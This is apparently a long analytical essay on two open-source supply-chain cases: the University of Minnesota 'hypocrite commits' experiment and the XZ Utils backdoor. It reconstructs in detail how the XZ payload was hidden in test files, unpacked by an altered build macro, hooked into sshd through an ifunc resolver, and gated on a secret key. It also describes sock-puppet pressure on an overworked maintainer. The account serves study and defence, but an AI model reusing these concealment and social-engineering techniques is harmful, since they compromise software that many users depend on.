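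Wu and Lu had expected the new error message to refer to a device whose memory other code might already have released. The Linux Foundation Technical Advisory Board concluded that they had misunderstood how the kernel manages such devices, and could not explain why the paper still presented the patch as flawed. After the maintainer accepted the patch, Wu and Lu asked about it and learned that it was fine. It then became a commit in the main kernel, contrary to what they wrote, even though their safeguard was supposed to keep out any accepted patch. This was the one time the safeguard mattered, but if the flaw had been real, the maintainer might have answered their question differently.

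Maintainers accepted none of the three bad patches. According to an LWN article that destinyland quotes at length in *Linux Stops Reverting Most University of Minnesota Patches, Admits Good Faith*, the planted bug was not always the reason. In *Looking back at the UMN episode*, a reviewer posting as error27 (2021) described finding other bugs in a patch, after which the researchers told the reviewer that the review had missed a use-after-free. The reviewer replied that there wasn't one, because the calling code held a reference that kept the memory from being freed, but the researchers disagreed. If the reviewer was right, Wu and Lu had failed to plant the intended flaw in two of their four patches.

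### What three rejections can show

The board concluded that kernel review had "worked as intended", while Wu and Lu had concluded from the same test that hypocrite commits were practical. Three patches give little support to either conclusion. If maintainers accepted half of all such patches, they would still reject three in a row one time in eight. Jones, who blogs about evidence in software engineering, also objected that three submissions are too few for meaningful statistics. The Braz experiments, by comparison, had about 150 reviewers each.

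The patches were not a fair sample of what an attacker could send. Wu and Lu picked them from 200 candidates because they looked hard to detect, but one copied an earlier bad patch that was notorious among kernel developers, and another contained no flaw. A patient attacker who knew one driver well could probably do better. Wu and Lu were experienced, though. They wrote in *Clarifications on the “hypocrite commit” work (FAQ)* (2020) that their group had found and fixed more than a thousand kernel bugs. Their failures suggest that completing an immature vulnerability is harder than finding something that looks like one.

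The result also depends on what counts as catching a patch. A reviewer who rejects a patch for an unrelated mistake keeps the hidden flaw out, at least for the moment, but an attacker could correct the mistake and resubmit the patch with the flaw still in it. Kernel reviewers often help beginners, and two of the three rejections came with advice on how to fix the patch. A fair test would have recorded whether each reviewer noticed the planted flaw, and what happened to a corrected version.

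Wu and Lu argue that a rejected attacker can try again with a different patch. If reviewers caught 80% of flawed patches and each attempt were independent, an attacker who sent five would have about a two-in-three chance of getting at least one accepted. Real attempts are not independent, because a suspicious patch can discredit the sender. Developers reviewing the patch of 9 August recognised James Bond as a false name, and a maintainer later ignored the honest fix for that reason. But this protection was inconsistent, as the James Bond patch of 21 August still got an ordinary review and friendly advice. An attacker can also open a new email account for free.

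Even an accepted patch would have shown only part of what an attack requires. Wu and Lu say that their use-after-free flaws might not have been exploitable, and they did not try to exploit them. An attacker needs a flaw that gives some control when triggered on a victim's machine. The test also did not cover a flaw assembled from many separate commits, which security researcher r00t4dm (2021) raised as a worry when the news broke.

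### Consent and the ethics board

The first objections came in November 2020, well before the ban, when Lu posted the paper's abstract on Twitter after a leading security conference run by the engineering association IEEE had accepted it. Sarah Jamie Lewis, who directs a privacy research organisation, questioned its ethics. On 1 December, she and three other security specialists, Linderud, Torres-Arias and René Mayrhofer, wrote to the conference's chairs. In *Ethics concerns about paper accepted for publication*, they argued that the researchers had experimented on open-source developers with no sign of approval from an ethics board. They also doubted that withdrawing a bad patch would make it safe, because automatic tools that copy changes from the main kernel into older versions might copy a flawed commit without the later one that corrected it.

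American universities have institutional review boards, which decide whether research involves human subjects and, if it does, whether it may go ahead. Wu and Lu consulted theirs only after they had sent the patches and the criticism had begun. The board gave them a letter exempting the work on the grounds that it was not research on people. The paper mentions the letter but not that it came after the experiment. In the FAQ, Wu and Lu apologised for not consulting the board first and wrote that researchers should always leave the decision to the board.

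They argued in their defence that they had studied a process, not individuals. They had collected no personal information, and they had used an anonymous account partly so that nobody could search for their emails and identify the maintainers. They admitted that the test had wasted maintainers' time, but said they had kept the patches short and could not think of a better method. On Twitter, Lu had earlier described the work as ordinary bug fixing done in two steps.

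It is hard to separate the review process from the people in this case, because the researchers wanted to know whether particular maintainers, reading particular emails, would be deceived. The Technical Advisory Board wrote that the reviewer of one bad patch had taken time to teach a sender who seemed to be a novice but already knew the patch was wrong. The false names were a problem in themselves, because everyone who submits a kernel patch must agree to a legal statement about its origin.

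Readers of LWN's *The TAB report on the UMN affair* (2021) argued about how serious the breach was. Mayrhofer wrote that wasted time is a harm and that a study that deceives people needs independent oversight. Another reader thought it absurd to invoke rules written for medical experiments, and pointed out that companies send staff fake phishing emails without asking each person first. A third replied that somebody senior authorises those emails and employees usually accept such tests as a condition of the job. Nobody responsible for the kernel had given permission for the researchers' test, although they could have asked a few senior developers without telling the reviewers.

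Theodore Ts'o, then a member of the Technical Advisory Board, suggested in the same discussion that the university had a reason to deny that this was human research. Public grants had paid for the work, and he thought the university might have to return money if it admitted this. He offered no evidence that this motive influenced the decision.

### The ban and the re-review

On 6 April 2021, another Minnesota researcher, Aditya Pakki, sent the kernel list a faulty patch. *Intentionally buggy commits for fame—and papers* (Edge, 2021) recounts how one developer questioned it the next day and another rejected it the day after. On 20 April, Greg Kroah-Hartman, who maintains the kernel's stable versions, accused Pakki of continuing the experiment. Pakki replied that the patch came from a new bug-finding tool that was not yet very accurate. Kroah-Hartman didn't believe him, so he told maintainers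 to reject anything from the university's addresses by default and prepared to remove 190 earlier commits.

On 21 April, the University of Minnesota's computer science department wrote in its *Statement from CS&E on Linux Kernel research* (2021) that its leaders had learned the details of the research that day. The department suspended the work and promised to investigate both the method and how the university had approved it. By the next day, the Technical Advisory Board had said that the recent patches appeared to have been submitted in good faith. The ban would not have stopped Wu and Lu, who had not used university addresses for their test, and it affected colleagues who had nothing to do with the test.

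Slashdot's *University of Minnesota Researchers Send Apology to Linux Kernel Mailing List* excerpts the researchers' open letter of 24 April, in which they apologised for using the community as a subject without its knowledge or permission. The Linux Foundation had asked them to identify the test patches and withdraw the paper. They withdrew it on 26 April and published the details the following day.

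Some kernel developers thought their own side had also behaved badly. Machek (2021) pointed out that nobody at Minnesota had deceived anyone in 2021, yet as late as 29 April Kroah-Hartman was still saying that commits from the university's addresses had been submitted in bad faith. Machek asked whether the developers owed an apology too. Cook (2021), who had posted the board's findings, agreed that the wording should have separated deliberate flaws from honest mistakes, but left it to Kroah-Hartman to decide whether to apologise.

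Meanwhile, developers re-examined 435 commits, covering every known kernel commit by the people who had written the group's papers and a few older ones from the university. The board classed 349 as correct and 39 as needing removal or repair. Other developers had fixed or removed 25 before the dispute, and one more had a removal request from its author. Another 12 no longer mattered because the code they changed was gone, and nine were older than the research group. In TechRadar's *More than 80 Linux devs called on to help to fix 'mess'*, Kroah-Hartman thanked more than 80 developers for their help. He removed 37 commits instead of the 190 he had first proposed.

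One of the 39 was the harmless George Acosta patch, which the board listed for removal because of the false name. The other 38 were faulty. Adding the 25 already dealt with and the one withdrawn by its author brings the total to 64, so about one in seven of the commits that developers re-examined had been wrong when a maintainer accepted it. One of the 38, a supposed fix for a memory leak, dated from December 2018.

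The 64 faulty patches are better evidence about kernel review than the live test is. They were sent in good faith and reviewed in the usual way, and many were small fixes of the kind that Wu and Lu recommend as cover. But they cannot be used to calculate a catch rate, because the board did not count the faulty patches that maintainers rejected or establish how many of the 64 made the kernel less secure.

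The board advised the university to have an experienced developer check its patches before sending them. Guenter Roeck, a kernel developer whom Edge quotes, told Lu that he was now much less inclined to accept small fixes from strangers. Such caution would make an attack like Wu and Lu's harder, but it would not prevent maintainers' own mistakes, which accounted for more than a third of the vulnerabilities in Wu and Lu's collection.

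## XZ Utils: how a stranger became a maintainer

XZ Utils had one maintainer, Lasse Collin, who worked on it without pay and had more patches waiting than he could handle. This made it harder for XZ Utils to turn down small fixes from strangers than it is for a project as large as the Linux kernel.

Between 2005 and 2008, Collin, with some help, designed the compressed file format that XZ Utils reads and writes. A file in this format takes up about 70% of the space that gzip, the older standard tool, needs, according to *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (Cox, 2024). Smaller files download faster, and developers built the format into much of Linux. *On the critical path to implant backdoors* (Lins, Mayrhofer and colleagues, 2024) mentions its use in the programs that install packages on Debian and Red Hat systems, and in the kernel, which can use the format to unpack its own code at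 startup. Other programs read and write the format through liblzma, a library included in XZ Utils. *Human-Certified Module Repositories for the AI Age* (2026) cites an analysis in which nearly 30,000 Debian and Ubuntu packages used XZ Utils.

Few people worked on XZ Utils. *Beneath the Mask* (Nealon, 2025) counted 29 contributors over the project's whole history, compared with 307 for libarchive, a library that reads and writes archive files. *Wolves in the Repository* (Przymus and Durieux, 2025) reports that about ten people were active in the XZ chat channel and that development had nearly stopped before Jia Tan arrived.

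### The first patches

Somebody opened the GitHub account JiaT75 in January 2021. Later that year, a person using the name Jia Tan sent two harmless changes to the XZ mailing list. The first, on 29 October, was a small settings file that tells text editors how to lay out the code, and the second, a month later, fixed a build problem. On 7 February 2022, Collin merged the first commit with Jia Tan's email address as author. It added checks for missing values. Some timelines give other dates for the first commit, partly because Git records when someone wrote a change separately from when someone committed it.

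In November 2021, JiaT75 had also sent a change to libarchive. File names in an archive can contain control characters that alter what a terminal displays, and libarchive had its own function, safe_fprintf, for printing such text safely. The change replaced it with the standard C function fprintf, which prints text unchanged. A maintainer approved and merged the change. Schneier's *XZ Utils Backdoor* quotes an Ars Technica report that calls it suspicious in retrospect and adds that no one noticed at the time.

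The reviewer could have spotted the problem from the diff alone, unlike with Wu and Lu's use-after-free patches, because the diff showed the word "safe" being removed. But a newcomer could easily have made the same change in good faith, since every C programmer knows fprintf and few would know libarchive's substitute. Lins and colleagues could not establish whether the change was connected to the attack on XZ Utils, and the later backdoor did not depend on it. The change may have been a test of how closely reviewers read, or just a poor patch.

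### The emails of 2022

On 19 April 2022, Jia Tan sent the XZ list a patch for converting compression settings to and from text. Before the end of the month, Jigar Kumar, a newcomer to the list, complained that Collin had not merged it. "Patches spend years on this mailing list," he wrote. By then, Collin had merged four of Jia Tan's patches.

On 19 May, another newcomer, Dennis Ens, politely asked whether anyone still maintained XZ for Java, Collin's companion project, which had not been updated for more than a year. Collin apologised the same day. He said that he had too little time, that something had to change, and that Jia Tan, who had been helping him privately, might have a bigger role in future.

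The tone then worsened. *Assessing the Y, and How, of the XZ Utils incident*, published on Securelist by the security company Kaspersky, reproduces six messages from Kumar. On 7 June he joined Ens's discussion, saying that nothing would happen until there was a new maintainer and that the current one had lost interest. Collin replied that he had not lost interest but that long-term mental health problems had limited what he could do, and reminded the list that this was "an unpaid hobby project". Kumar answered six days later, "Right now you choke your repo."

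On 21 June, Ens said he was sorry about Collin's mental health, then used it to argue that Collin should be aware of his limits and pass one of the two projects to someone else, because "the community desires more". The next day Kumar asked Jia Tan, "Why can't you commit this yourself?" A week later, Collin told the list that Jia Tan was "practically a co-maintainer already" and that a change in maintainership was under way.

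Cox concludes that the pressure worked. It probably helped, but Collin first mentioned a bigger role for Jia Tan on 19 May, when he had received only a couple of complaints from Kumar and a polite question from Ens. The harshest messages came in June. By then Jia Tan had been useful to him for months and the backlog was real, so the emails may have sped up a promotion that Jia Tan would have earned anyway.

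### Whether Kumar and Ens were real

Cox thinks both were probably fakes, and *Closing the Chain* (2025), a study of three major software security incidents, calls them suspected sock puppets, meaning false identities that make one party look like several. Brian Krebs, a security journalist, found that neither their email addresses nor Jia Tan's appeared anywhere else on the internet, even in large collections of stolen and leaked account data. That is unusual for a programmer. An engineer at ReversingLabs, a security company, points out that it is normally easy to connect a developer's account to an employer, a personal web page or a social media profile.

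Securelist adds that all three addresses came from free email services and followed a similar pattern, and that the three correspondents made similar spelling and grammar mistakes. Kumar and Ens also stopped writing to the list once Jia Tan's promotion was settled.

Accounts with the same kind of address appeared again in March 2024, when the attacker needed Linux distributions to adopt the backdoored release. A contributor called Hans Jansen asked Debian to update its package, and two unknown users supported him the next day, saying the new version would fix a bug that affected them. When a Debian developer objected to how Jansen was making the update, one of the two asked whether Debian could just fix the problem "instead of having a policy debate".

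None of this proves that one person or group wrote all the messages. A new email address would not appear in old stolen data, whoever owned it, and Przymus and Durieux found no direct link between the accounts. It was also not strange to post for a while and vanish, since six of the eight new people they counted on the list during this phase of the project were not active in any other phase. But two untraceable strangers made the same demand in the same weeks, in support of a third who turned out to be an attacker. It would be a remarkable coincidence if they were ordinary users. They were also fairly subtle, because neither suggested Jia Tan as a possible maintainer before Collin did.

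### Control of releases and the website

Jia Tan's role then grew over the next year and a half. The dates below are Cox's.

| Date | Step |
|---|---|
| 27 September 2022 | Jia Tan tells the mailing list what version 5.4.0 will contain |
| 30 November 2022 | Collin names Jia Tan as a maintainer in the readme and directs bug reports to both of them |
| 30 December 2022 | Jia Tan adds a batch of commits directly to the repository |
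| 18 March 2023 | Jia Tan makes a first release, version 5.4.2 |
| 20 March 2023 | Jia Tan becomes the contact for bugs found by OSS-Fuzz, Google's automatic testing service |
| 19 January 2024 | Jia Tan moves the project's website to GitHub and so gains control of it |
| 20 March 2024 | Collin asks kernel developers to list Jia Tan beside him as a maintainer of the kernel's XZ code |

The first release, 5.4.2, was partly Collin's work. According to his review notes on Tukaani, his website for the project, Jia Tan signed the tag but Collin built and signed the release archives. Jia Tan built the archives for the next four versions in the series, 5.4.3 to 5.4.6. Collin later checked these and found nothing malicious, so packagers had received several good releases from Jia Tan before the first bad one.

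The move to GitHub mattered as much as commit rights. Przymus and Durieux say that Jia Tan created the project's GitHub organisation and repository in December 2022, which would have made Jia Tan their owner. Cox says that Collin's organisation already existed in October, when Jia Tan joined it. Przymus and Durieux also found that the request that led to the website's move came from an account with no credible history. In his statement on Tukaani (2024), Collin says that nobody else ever had access to the main tukaani.org site or the repositories there, and that Jia Tan could reach only what GitHub hosted.

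Collin continued to review Jia Tan's work after Jia Tan had commit rights. His notes mention a change that stayed on a separate branch until he gave permission to merge it, and another that reached the main code with an error because his comments in the chat came slightly too late. He rewrote a good deal of what Jia Tan sent. He sometimes yielded on matters of taste, including some additions to the code that he thought were useless: "He kept insisting on them so eventually I gave in."

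Collin also checked release archives. Before version 5.4.5 became official, he noticed that its archives recorded the wrong file owners and permissions. The obvious explanation was that Jia Tan had typed the wrong build command, but Jia Tan would not admit to such a simple mistake. Collin compared their contents with an archive he had made himself, found nothing else wrong, and let the release go ahead.

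### Could anyone have told Jia Tan from a keen newcomer?

Przymus and Durieux examined 1,020 commits, 307 mailing list messages and nearly 3,000 GitHub events. They found that Jia Tan changed more lines of documentation and translations than of the program itself. Jia Tan started with code in 2022, then in 2023 mostly took over chores, including translations, the build system, release announcements and users' questions. Przymus and Durieux regard these chores as an easy way to build credibility, since they require less expertise than programming and attract less scrutiny.

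They are also what an overworked maintainer most wants help with. Only eight commits were malicious, all in 2024. Nealon's figures imply that Jia Tan wrote about 500 of the project's commits, so roughly one in sixty was part of the attack. When Collin reviewed the rest, he marked many of them "OK". The bugs and clumsy code he found were ordinary, and some of the work was good, including a large change to the decompression code that he had requested.

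The project also seemed to be recovering. In the phase that began when Collin accepted Jia Tan's first commit, 65 commits included thanks to a contributor, compared with an earlier median of 16 a year. Przymus and Durieux point to possible warning signs, such as a sudden growth in expertise and an unusual amount of time spent on the project, but concede that these are "often indistinguishable" from the habits of enthusiastic, skilled contributors.

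Hindsight can also make innocent work look sinister. Przymus and Durieux suspect that Jia Tan pushed aside the volunteer translators and used automatic translation, given how many languages were involved. Collin compared the project's translations with the translators' own files and could explain the differences, many of which were spacing adjustments. He had also agreed to one of the changes in how the project handled translations, because it made it possible to correct a typo in the last days before a release.

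Nealon, a security engineer at GitLab, compared XZ Utils with 19 similar projects. Nealon first searched for people who had merged their own pull requests without review less than two years after their first commit. Excluding long-standing contributors left four of the 1,996 people who had opened a pull request. One was JiaT75, who had first merged a pull request this way after ten months. Nealon then searched for people who had written more than 5% of a project's commits but had been present for less than 20% of its history. Four people met these criteria, including JiaT75, who had written 17.4% of the commits in 12.5% of the history.

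The two searches flagged five people besides JiaT75, all of them legitimate. One looked more suspicious than JiaT75 by that measure, having started merging unreviewed changes after only two months and merged 43 to JiaT75's 24. The previous maintainer had met this person and handed over the project, which explains the record. Nealon set the thresholds with JiaT75's record in view, so it is unsurprising that the searches found that account, and neither has caught a previously unknown attacker. Still, the first search could have prompted questions about JiaT75 in December 2022, over a year before the backdoor, and there were few enough names for a person to follow up each one.

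Nealon cleared the five using evidence other than their pattern of work, such as an employer's email address, a listing on an established project's website or the meeting with the former maintainer. Jia Tan had nothing comparable. Lins and colleagues discuss asking for proof of identity before promoting someone to maintainer. Debian already requires its package maintainers to meet other maintainers in person and show identification. Such a rule would have seriously hindered Jia Tan, but an attacker can steal an identity or bribe someone with a genuine one, and some honest developers have good reasons to stay anonymous. Collin would also have had to turn away the only person offering sustained help.

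### Who was behind the name

Nobody has publicly identified the attacker. *Half a Second* (Mastronardi, 2026), a book about the case last updated in July 2026, says the attacker remains unknown and may never be found.

Many people suspect that a government was behind the backdoor because it took patience and skill, but there is little public evidence. The list of authors that now comes with XZ Utils, and with FreeBSD's copy of it, attributes the backdoor to Jia Tan and "the team behind him". Securelist found some support for a team in the timing of JiaT75's commits. The account made its malicious commits in February and March 2024 at times that did not match its earlier habits. A second person might have taken over the account, or a team might have divided the work, but one person in a hurry would also work at unusual times.

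Securelist considers the possibility that Jia Tan was an honest contributor whom somebody manipulated in early 2024. This would explain why so much of the earlier work was sound, but it would also mean that the 2022 emails came from unrelated people by coincidence, which is hard to believe.

Jia Tan's location is also unclear. The only public trace is an internet address in Singapore that Jia Tan may have used to join the project's chat on 29 March 2024, and it belonged to a VPN, a service that hides where its users are. A few of Jia Tan's commits record a time zone two or three hours ahead of UTC, unlike most of the others. In *Analysis on who is Jia Tan, and who he could work for*, Colomar (2024) suspected that Jia Tan made these commits during visits to an intelligence agency. Two days later, Colomar admitted a mistake in the analysis, which a script by Bachmeyer (2024) in the same discussion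 had revealed.

A more ordinary explanation is that some commits under Jia Tan's name carry Collin's time zone. Collin lives in Finland, which is two hours ahead of UTC in winter and three in summer, and he says that he and Jia Tan sometimes recorded commits in each other's names by agreement. A programmer can also set a commit's time zone to anything. Margin Research's *Better Analyzing Foreign Adversary Threats to Open-Source Software* (2025) says that time zone data can only occasionally help identify a contributor's country and that people can manipulate it.

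The Nightly, an Australian news site, reported that a Chinese citizen, whom it described as the son of a senior official, had boasted in an online chat of carrying out the attack. No public evidence corroborates the claim.

Collin probably knows more about Jia Tan than anyone else who is willing to talk, because they did much of their work together in private messages that outside researchers have not seen. Neither he nor Jia Tan answered questions from The Intercept (2024). Collin has promised an article on how the backdoor got into the releases, but according to his website in August 2026, it was still taking much longer than he had expected.

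## XZ Utils: how the backdoor was assembled

On 24 February 2024, Jia Tan released version 5.6.0 of XZ Utils with a backdoor in it. The backdoor targeted sshd, the part of OpenSSH that lets people log in to a Linux machine over a network. Anyone with a particular secret key could run commands on an affected server with full control of the machine, without logging in first.

Jia Tan put most of the harmful code in the public repository, disguised as test data, where it did nothing by itself. The short piece of code that activated it was only in the release archives. Freund (2024), the engineer who discovered the backdoor, described most of its main parts in a single email, *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, and others have since analyzed the code in more detail.

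### Why a login program loaded a compression library

OpenSSH's own code does not use liblzma, the library in XZ Utils. But Debian and several other distributions modify sshd to work with systemd, the program that starts and supervises other programs on most Linux systems. The modified sshd sends systemd a short message when it has finished starting. According to Przymus and Durieux, the preferred way to send this message is to call a function in a library named libsystemd. That library also reads compressed system logs, for which it needed liblzma.

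When Linux starts a program, it loads the libraries the program uses, and then the libraries those libraries use. All of this code runs as part of the program, with the same rights. On the modified systems, liblzma was therefore loaded into sshd at startup, although sshd never used it to compress anything. *Timeline of the xz open source attack* lists Debian, Ubuntu and Fedora among the distributions that modified sshd, and Arch Linux, Gentoo and NixOS among those that did not.

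This indirect route suited an attacker because many specialists watch OpenSSH closely, whereas XZ Utils had one overworked maintainer and one helper. Anyone reviewing a change to XZ Utils would also have had little reason to think about remote logins.

### The payload in the test files

XZ Utils has a directory of unusual and damaged compressed files that its developers use to check that the decompressor handles them correctly. The directory existed long before Jia Tan arrived. According to its readme, people had made many of the files by hand, byte by byte, so there was no better source code for them than the files themselves.

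On 23 February 2024, the day before the release of 5.6.0, Jia Tan committed five more test files. The full commit message, according to the change log Collin (2026) published with version 5.8.3, was "Tests: Add a few test files." The commit also added 19 lines to the readme. The log's timestamps show that Jia Tan committed the release notes for 5.6.0 less than 17 hours later.

Two of the five files contained the attack. The larger, good-large_compressed.lzma, was 35,430 bytes long and decompressed without errors. Inside it, blocks of meaningless filler alternated with blocks of the payload. In *xz/liblzma: Bash-stage Obfuscation Explained*, the security researcher Coldwind (2024) found that the first block of filler was the letter A repeated 1,024 times. The payload blocks looked like random noise because the attacker had compressed and encrypted them. A mixture of repetition and noise is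 reasonable test data for a compression program, so even someone who looked at the contents might not have been suspicious.

The smaller file, bad-3-corrupt_lzma2.xz, was 484 bytes. An XZ file can hold several compressed streams one after another, and this one was correctly described in the readme as having three, with corrupt data in the middle one. The attacker had corrupted a compressed script by swapping the byte values for tabs and spaces, and those for hyphens and underscores, throughout. Anyone who knew about the swap could reverse it with one standard command.

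Collin explains in his review notes on Tukaani that the test script picks up every file in the directory whose name fits a pattern, so adding these files was enough to have them tested. Freund had written that the project's tests did not even use them in 5.6.0, but a reviewer would not have found them unused. The file named "good" decompressed and the one named "bad" was damaged, as their names indicated.

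The first two of the eight malicious commits, from January 2024, had already added and then replaced a pair of test files for RISC-V, a type of processor. Those files contained a genuine test, but Collin writes that it would have fitted into much smaller ones, and it is not clear what the rest of their contents was for. The scripts that Coldwind and Cox examined extract the backdoor from the two February files and do not read the RISC-V ones.

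Collin, who designed the .xz format and knew it better than almost anyone, looked at the RISC-V files but commented only on one of their compression settings. Jia Tan then replaced the files, and Collin now thinks his comment provided a good excuse to update something hidden in them.

### The altered macro in the release archive

The instructions for unpacking the payload were in build-to-host.m4, a file that Jia Tan put in the release archives but not in the repository.

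Nobody thought an extra file in the release archive strange because most complex Unix software, including XZ Utils, puts build files there that are not in the repository. XZ Utils uses GNU Autoconf, a tool that generates a build script named configure. This script examines the computer, for instance to find its compiler, and then writes a Makefile, a list of instructions that the rest of the build follows. Autoconf assembles configure partly from macros, which are reusable pieces of script in files ending in .m4. The release archive includes configure and many of these macros so that packagers can build the program without running Autoconf themselves.

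The GNU project publishes a genuine macro called build-to-host.m4. According to Collin's notes, the ordinary steps for preparing a release copy this file into the archive along with several others. Freund observed that XZ Utils did not use it in the repository, but somebody who compared the two would have expected to find it only in the archive. To notice anything wrong, they would have had to compare the file with the GNU project's copy.

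Even then, the changes did not stand out. Cox's second article on the attack, *The xz attack shell script* (2024), prints the differences, about thirty new lines. Jia Tan had raised the version number, extended the copyright date to 2024 and written comments in the style of the original. Build macros are notoriously hard to read, and Cox thinks the changes would have looked fairly plausible "in case anyone thought to check".

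The new lines searched the whole source tree for a pattern of symbols that occurred only in the small "corrupt" file, so they did not have to mention the test files by name. They took the name of the decompression program from the last two letters of the corrupt file's name and stored it in a variable whose name ended in "prefix". Other variables held further fragments of a command. When configure ran, it joined the fragments, swapped the byte values back, decompressed the repaired file with xz, and ran the resulting script. Unpacking the backdoor therefore required a working copy of XZ Utils, which a machine that builds Linux packages almost always has.

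Only some of the archives GitHub offered for version 5.6.0 contained the backdoor's trigger. Lins and colleagues explain that GitHub automatically makes two archives of the repository for every release, and these did not contain the altered macro. Jia Tan uploaded four more that did, each with a signature file that let packagers confirm who had made it. Packagers had good reason to prefer these four, because they included a ready-made configure script and came with a valid signature from one of the project's maintainers. Checking that signature would not have protected them from the backdoor.

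Securelist's *XZ backdoor story* instead says that the files on GitHub were harmless and only downloads from the project's website contained the macro. Like Lins and colleagues, Freund reports in his email that only GitHub's automatic archives were clean. Collin also states on Tukaani that Jia Tan created and signed the archives for this release, and that the trigger was never in the repository.

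### From the archive to the library

The script from the small file had one task, which was to extract a longer script from the large one. It decompressed the large file, threw away the filler and kept the other blocks, 33,492 bytes in all. The first 31,264 bytes were the encrypted backdoor, which it skipped for the time being. The remaining 2,228 bytes, after a simple letter-for-letter style of decoding and another decompression, became the second script. (Cox and Securelist both describe the script as filling the last 31,000 or so bytes, but Coldwind is right that this figure is the position where it begins.)

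This second script ran twice, which confused several people who tried to follow it. Fernhout (2024) worked out the order in a reply to Coldwind on a security mailing list. The script first ran as part of configure, when it checked its environment and, if that was suitable, added lines to the Makefile. Cox points out that it scattered these lines so that nobody would see them side by side, and used names that resembled the legitimate ones around them. The added lines ran the script again during the build, when it inserted the backdoor.

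If the surroundings were unsuitable, the script stopped quietly and the build produced a clean library. It continued only if all of these conditions held:

- The build was for Linux on x86-64 processors, the type in most servers.
- It used the GNU compiler and the GNU linker, the program that joins pieces of compiled code.
- It was producing a shared library with the ifunc feature turned on.
- It was part of making a package for Debian or for a distribution that uses RPM packages, such as Fedora.

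The last condition narrowed the attack to the distributions most likely to have modified sshd. Freund suspected it was also meant to hinder investigators. Someone who downloaded the bad archive and built it by hand got an ordinary copy of liblzma and could reasonably conclude that nothing was wrong.

In its second run, the script decrypted the backdoor and wrote it to disk as an object file of about 88 kilobytes. An object file is compiled code that is not yet part of a finished program. The file had the same name as a genuine object file in the build, except for a hyphen in place of an underscore.

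The script then had to make liblzma use the backdoor's object file. It slightly changed the text of crc64_fast.c, an XZ Utils source file. The main change was to a call to a function that checks which features the processor has. The script removed one of the two underscores at the start of the function's name, so that the call went to a function in the backdoor instead. It passed the changed text to the compiler without saving it, and the compiler combined the result with the object file. Finally, the script deleted its temporary files.

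A packager who read every line of C code in the archive, before or after the build, would not have found the change, because it existed only in the text passed between two programs. Neither the repository nor the archive ever contained the object file in a recognisable form. Cox says it would have looked suspicious if Jia Tan had simply committed it.

### Running before Linux locked the table

The backdoor was now part of liblzma, but it still had to take control of something in sshd, which doesn't call liblzma. It did this using ifunc, a feature that lets a library contain several versions of a function and choose one when a program starts.

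liblzma had an ordinary use for such a choice. XZ files contain checksums that reveal damage, and newer processors have special instructions for computing them quickly. The library therefore had a fast version of the checksum function and a general one. A small function called a resolver asked the processor what it supported and selected a version. Linux runs resolvers automatically while it loads a program, whether or not the program ever computes a checksum. The altered call was in the resolver, so the backdoor ran every time sshd started.

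The resolver also ran early enough for the backdoor to redirect function calls. A program keeps a table of the addresses of functions it uses from other libraries, which Linux fills in as the program loads. An attacker who can change an entry can make the program run something else. To protect against this, many distributions have Linux fill in the whole table at the start and then make it read-only. But resolvers run before the table becomes read-only, so their code can still change it. Filling in the whole table early also guaranteed that the resolver, and therefore the backdoor, would run early.

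Linux processed liblzma before it looked up the functions that sshd itself needed, so the entry that the backdoor had to change did not have its final value yet. Freund found that the backdoor got around this by attaching itself to an auditing feature of Linux's loader, which reports each function as the loader finds it. The backdoor waited for a function called RSA_public_decrypt, replaced that function's address with the address of its own code, and then detached itself from the auditing feature.

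Jia Tan had described the timing publicly in a commit message of 20 October 2023, which is in the log that Collin published. Jia Tan wrote that resolvers run so early that the mechanism for calling other functions may not be ready. This was the reason Jia Tan gave for moving some code, since programs that used liblzma could otherwise crash as they started. The problem was real and anyone who works on resolvers needs to know about it, so a reader at the time would probably have seen only a careful programmer.

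### What happened in the key check

Many administrators log in to servers with a pair of keys instead of a password. The user's computer signs a message with the private key, and sshd checks the signature with the public key. For RSA, a common type of key, sshd uses the function RSA_public_decrypt from the OpenSSL cryptographic library for part of this check. Once the backdoor had replaced that function's address with that of its own, its function received any key presented during a login attempt.

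An RSA public key contains a very large number, and the person who connects chooses which key to send. According to Przymus and Durieux, the backdoor looked for hidden instructions in that number. Lins and colleagues add that it acted on them only if they came from the holder of a specific private key. It then passed the attacker's command to a standard function that ran it on the machine. Przymus and Durieux also describe a way for the attacker to log in with any password.

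For everyone else, the backdoor called the normal library code and the login went ahead. Anyone who discovered the backdoor could not have used it on other servers without the private key. An administrator also could not have found it by sending a server odd requests and watching for strange replies.

The backdoor acted only inside sshd, and Freund found that it stayed inactive if sshd had been started from an ordinary terminal or with certain debugging settings. Securelist found an environment variable (a named setting passed to a program when it starts) that would turn the backdoor off. The code did not store the names of the functions it was looking for as readable text, so a search of the library for suspicious words would have found nothing.

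### The pieces and their dates

| Piece | Date | Stated reason | What a reviewer saw | What it did | Did the attack need it? |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| ifunc patches | 22 June 2023 | Faster checksums | Ordinary C code and build checks, which Collin partly rewrote | Made liblzma run a resolver while programs load | Yes, as designed |
| Fuzz-testing change | 7 July 2023 | ifunc conflicted with a memory checker | A request to Google's testing service to turn ifunc off | Kept automatic tests away from the ifunc code | Probably not |
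| Test files | 23 February 2024 | None beyond "Add a few test files" | Five binary files and 19 lines of readme | Held the scripts and the backdoor | Yes |
| Altered macro | 24 February 2024 | None, as it was never in a commit | Nothing in the repository but a line telling Git to ignore the file, added on 15 February | Unpacked and ran the first script | Yes |
| Broken Landlock check | 26 February 2024 | A more reliable check for a security feature | A sensible change of 54 added lines, one of them a lone full stop | Turned the feature off in some builds | No |

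Published timelines disagree about some of these dates. *Timeline of the xz open source attack* puts the Landlock change on 28 February and names Collin as the committer. The log gives 26 February, but that is the author's date, so Collin probably committed the change two days later. Lins and colleagues describe the test files before the instruction to ignore build-to-host.m4, but the log dates the instruction eight days earlier than the files.

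Accounts also differ on when the attack on the code began. Cox dates it to the test files of 23 February, while Przymus and Durieux date it to a commit of 22 January. The January date fits Collin's review better, because he identifies a commit from that month as the first to prepare for the backdoor.

The attacker may well have been writing the hidden code before then. On 11 January, Collin merged a reorganisation of the checksum code that renamed one of its files, and the second script checks for that file under its new name. Cox infers that an earlier version of the script looked for the old name and that the attacker had to update it. Collin recalls that Jia Tan did not like the reorganisation at first but changed their mind in January. An attacker who had to adapt hidden code would have had a reason to object, but programmers often object to such changes anyway.

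### Which pieces the attack needed

Collin classifies eight commits as malicious, but they contain only one of the three necessary pieces, the test files. The macro was never in a commit, and he does not count the ifunc patches as malicious.

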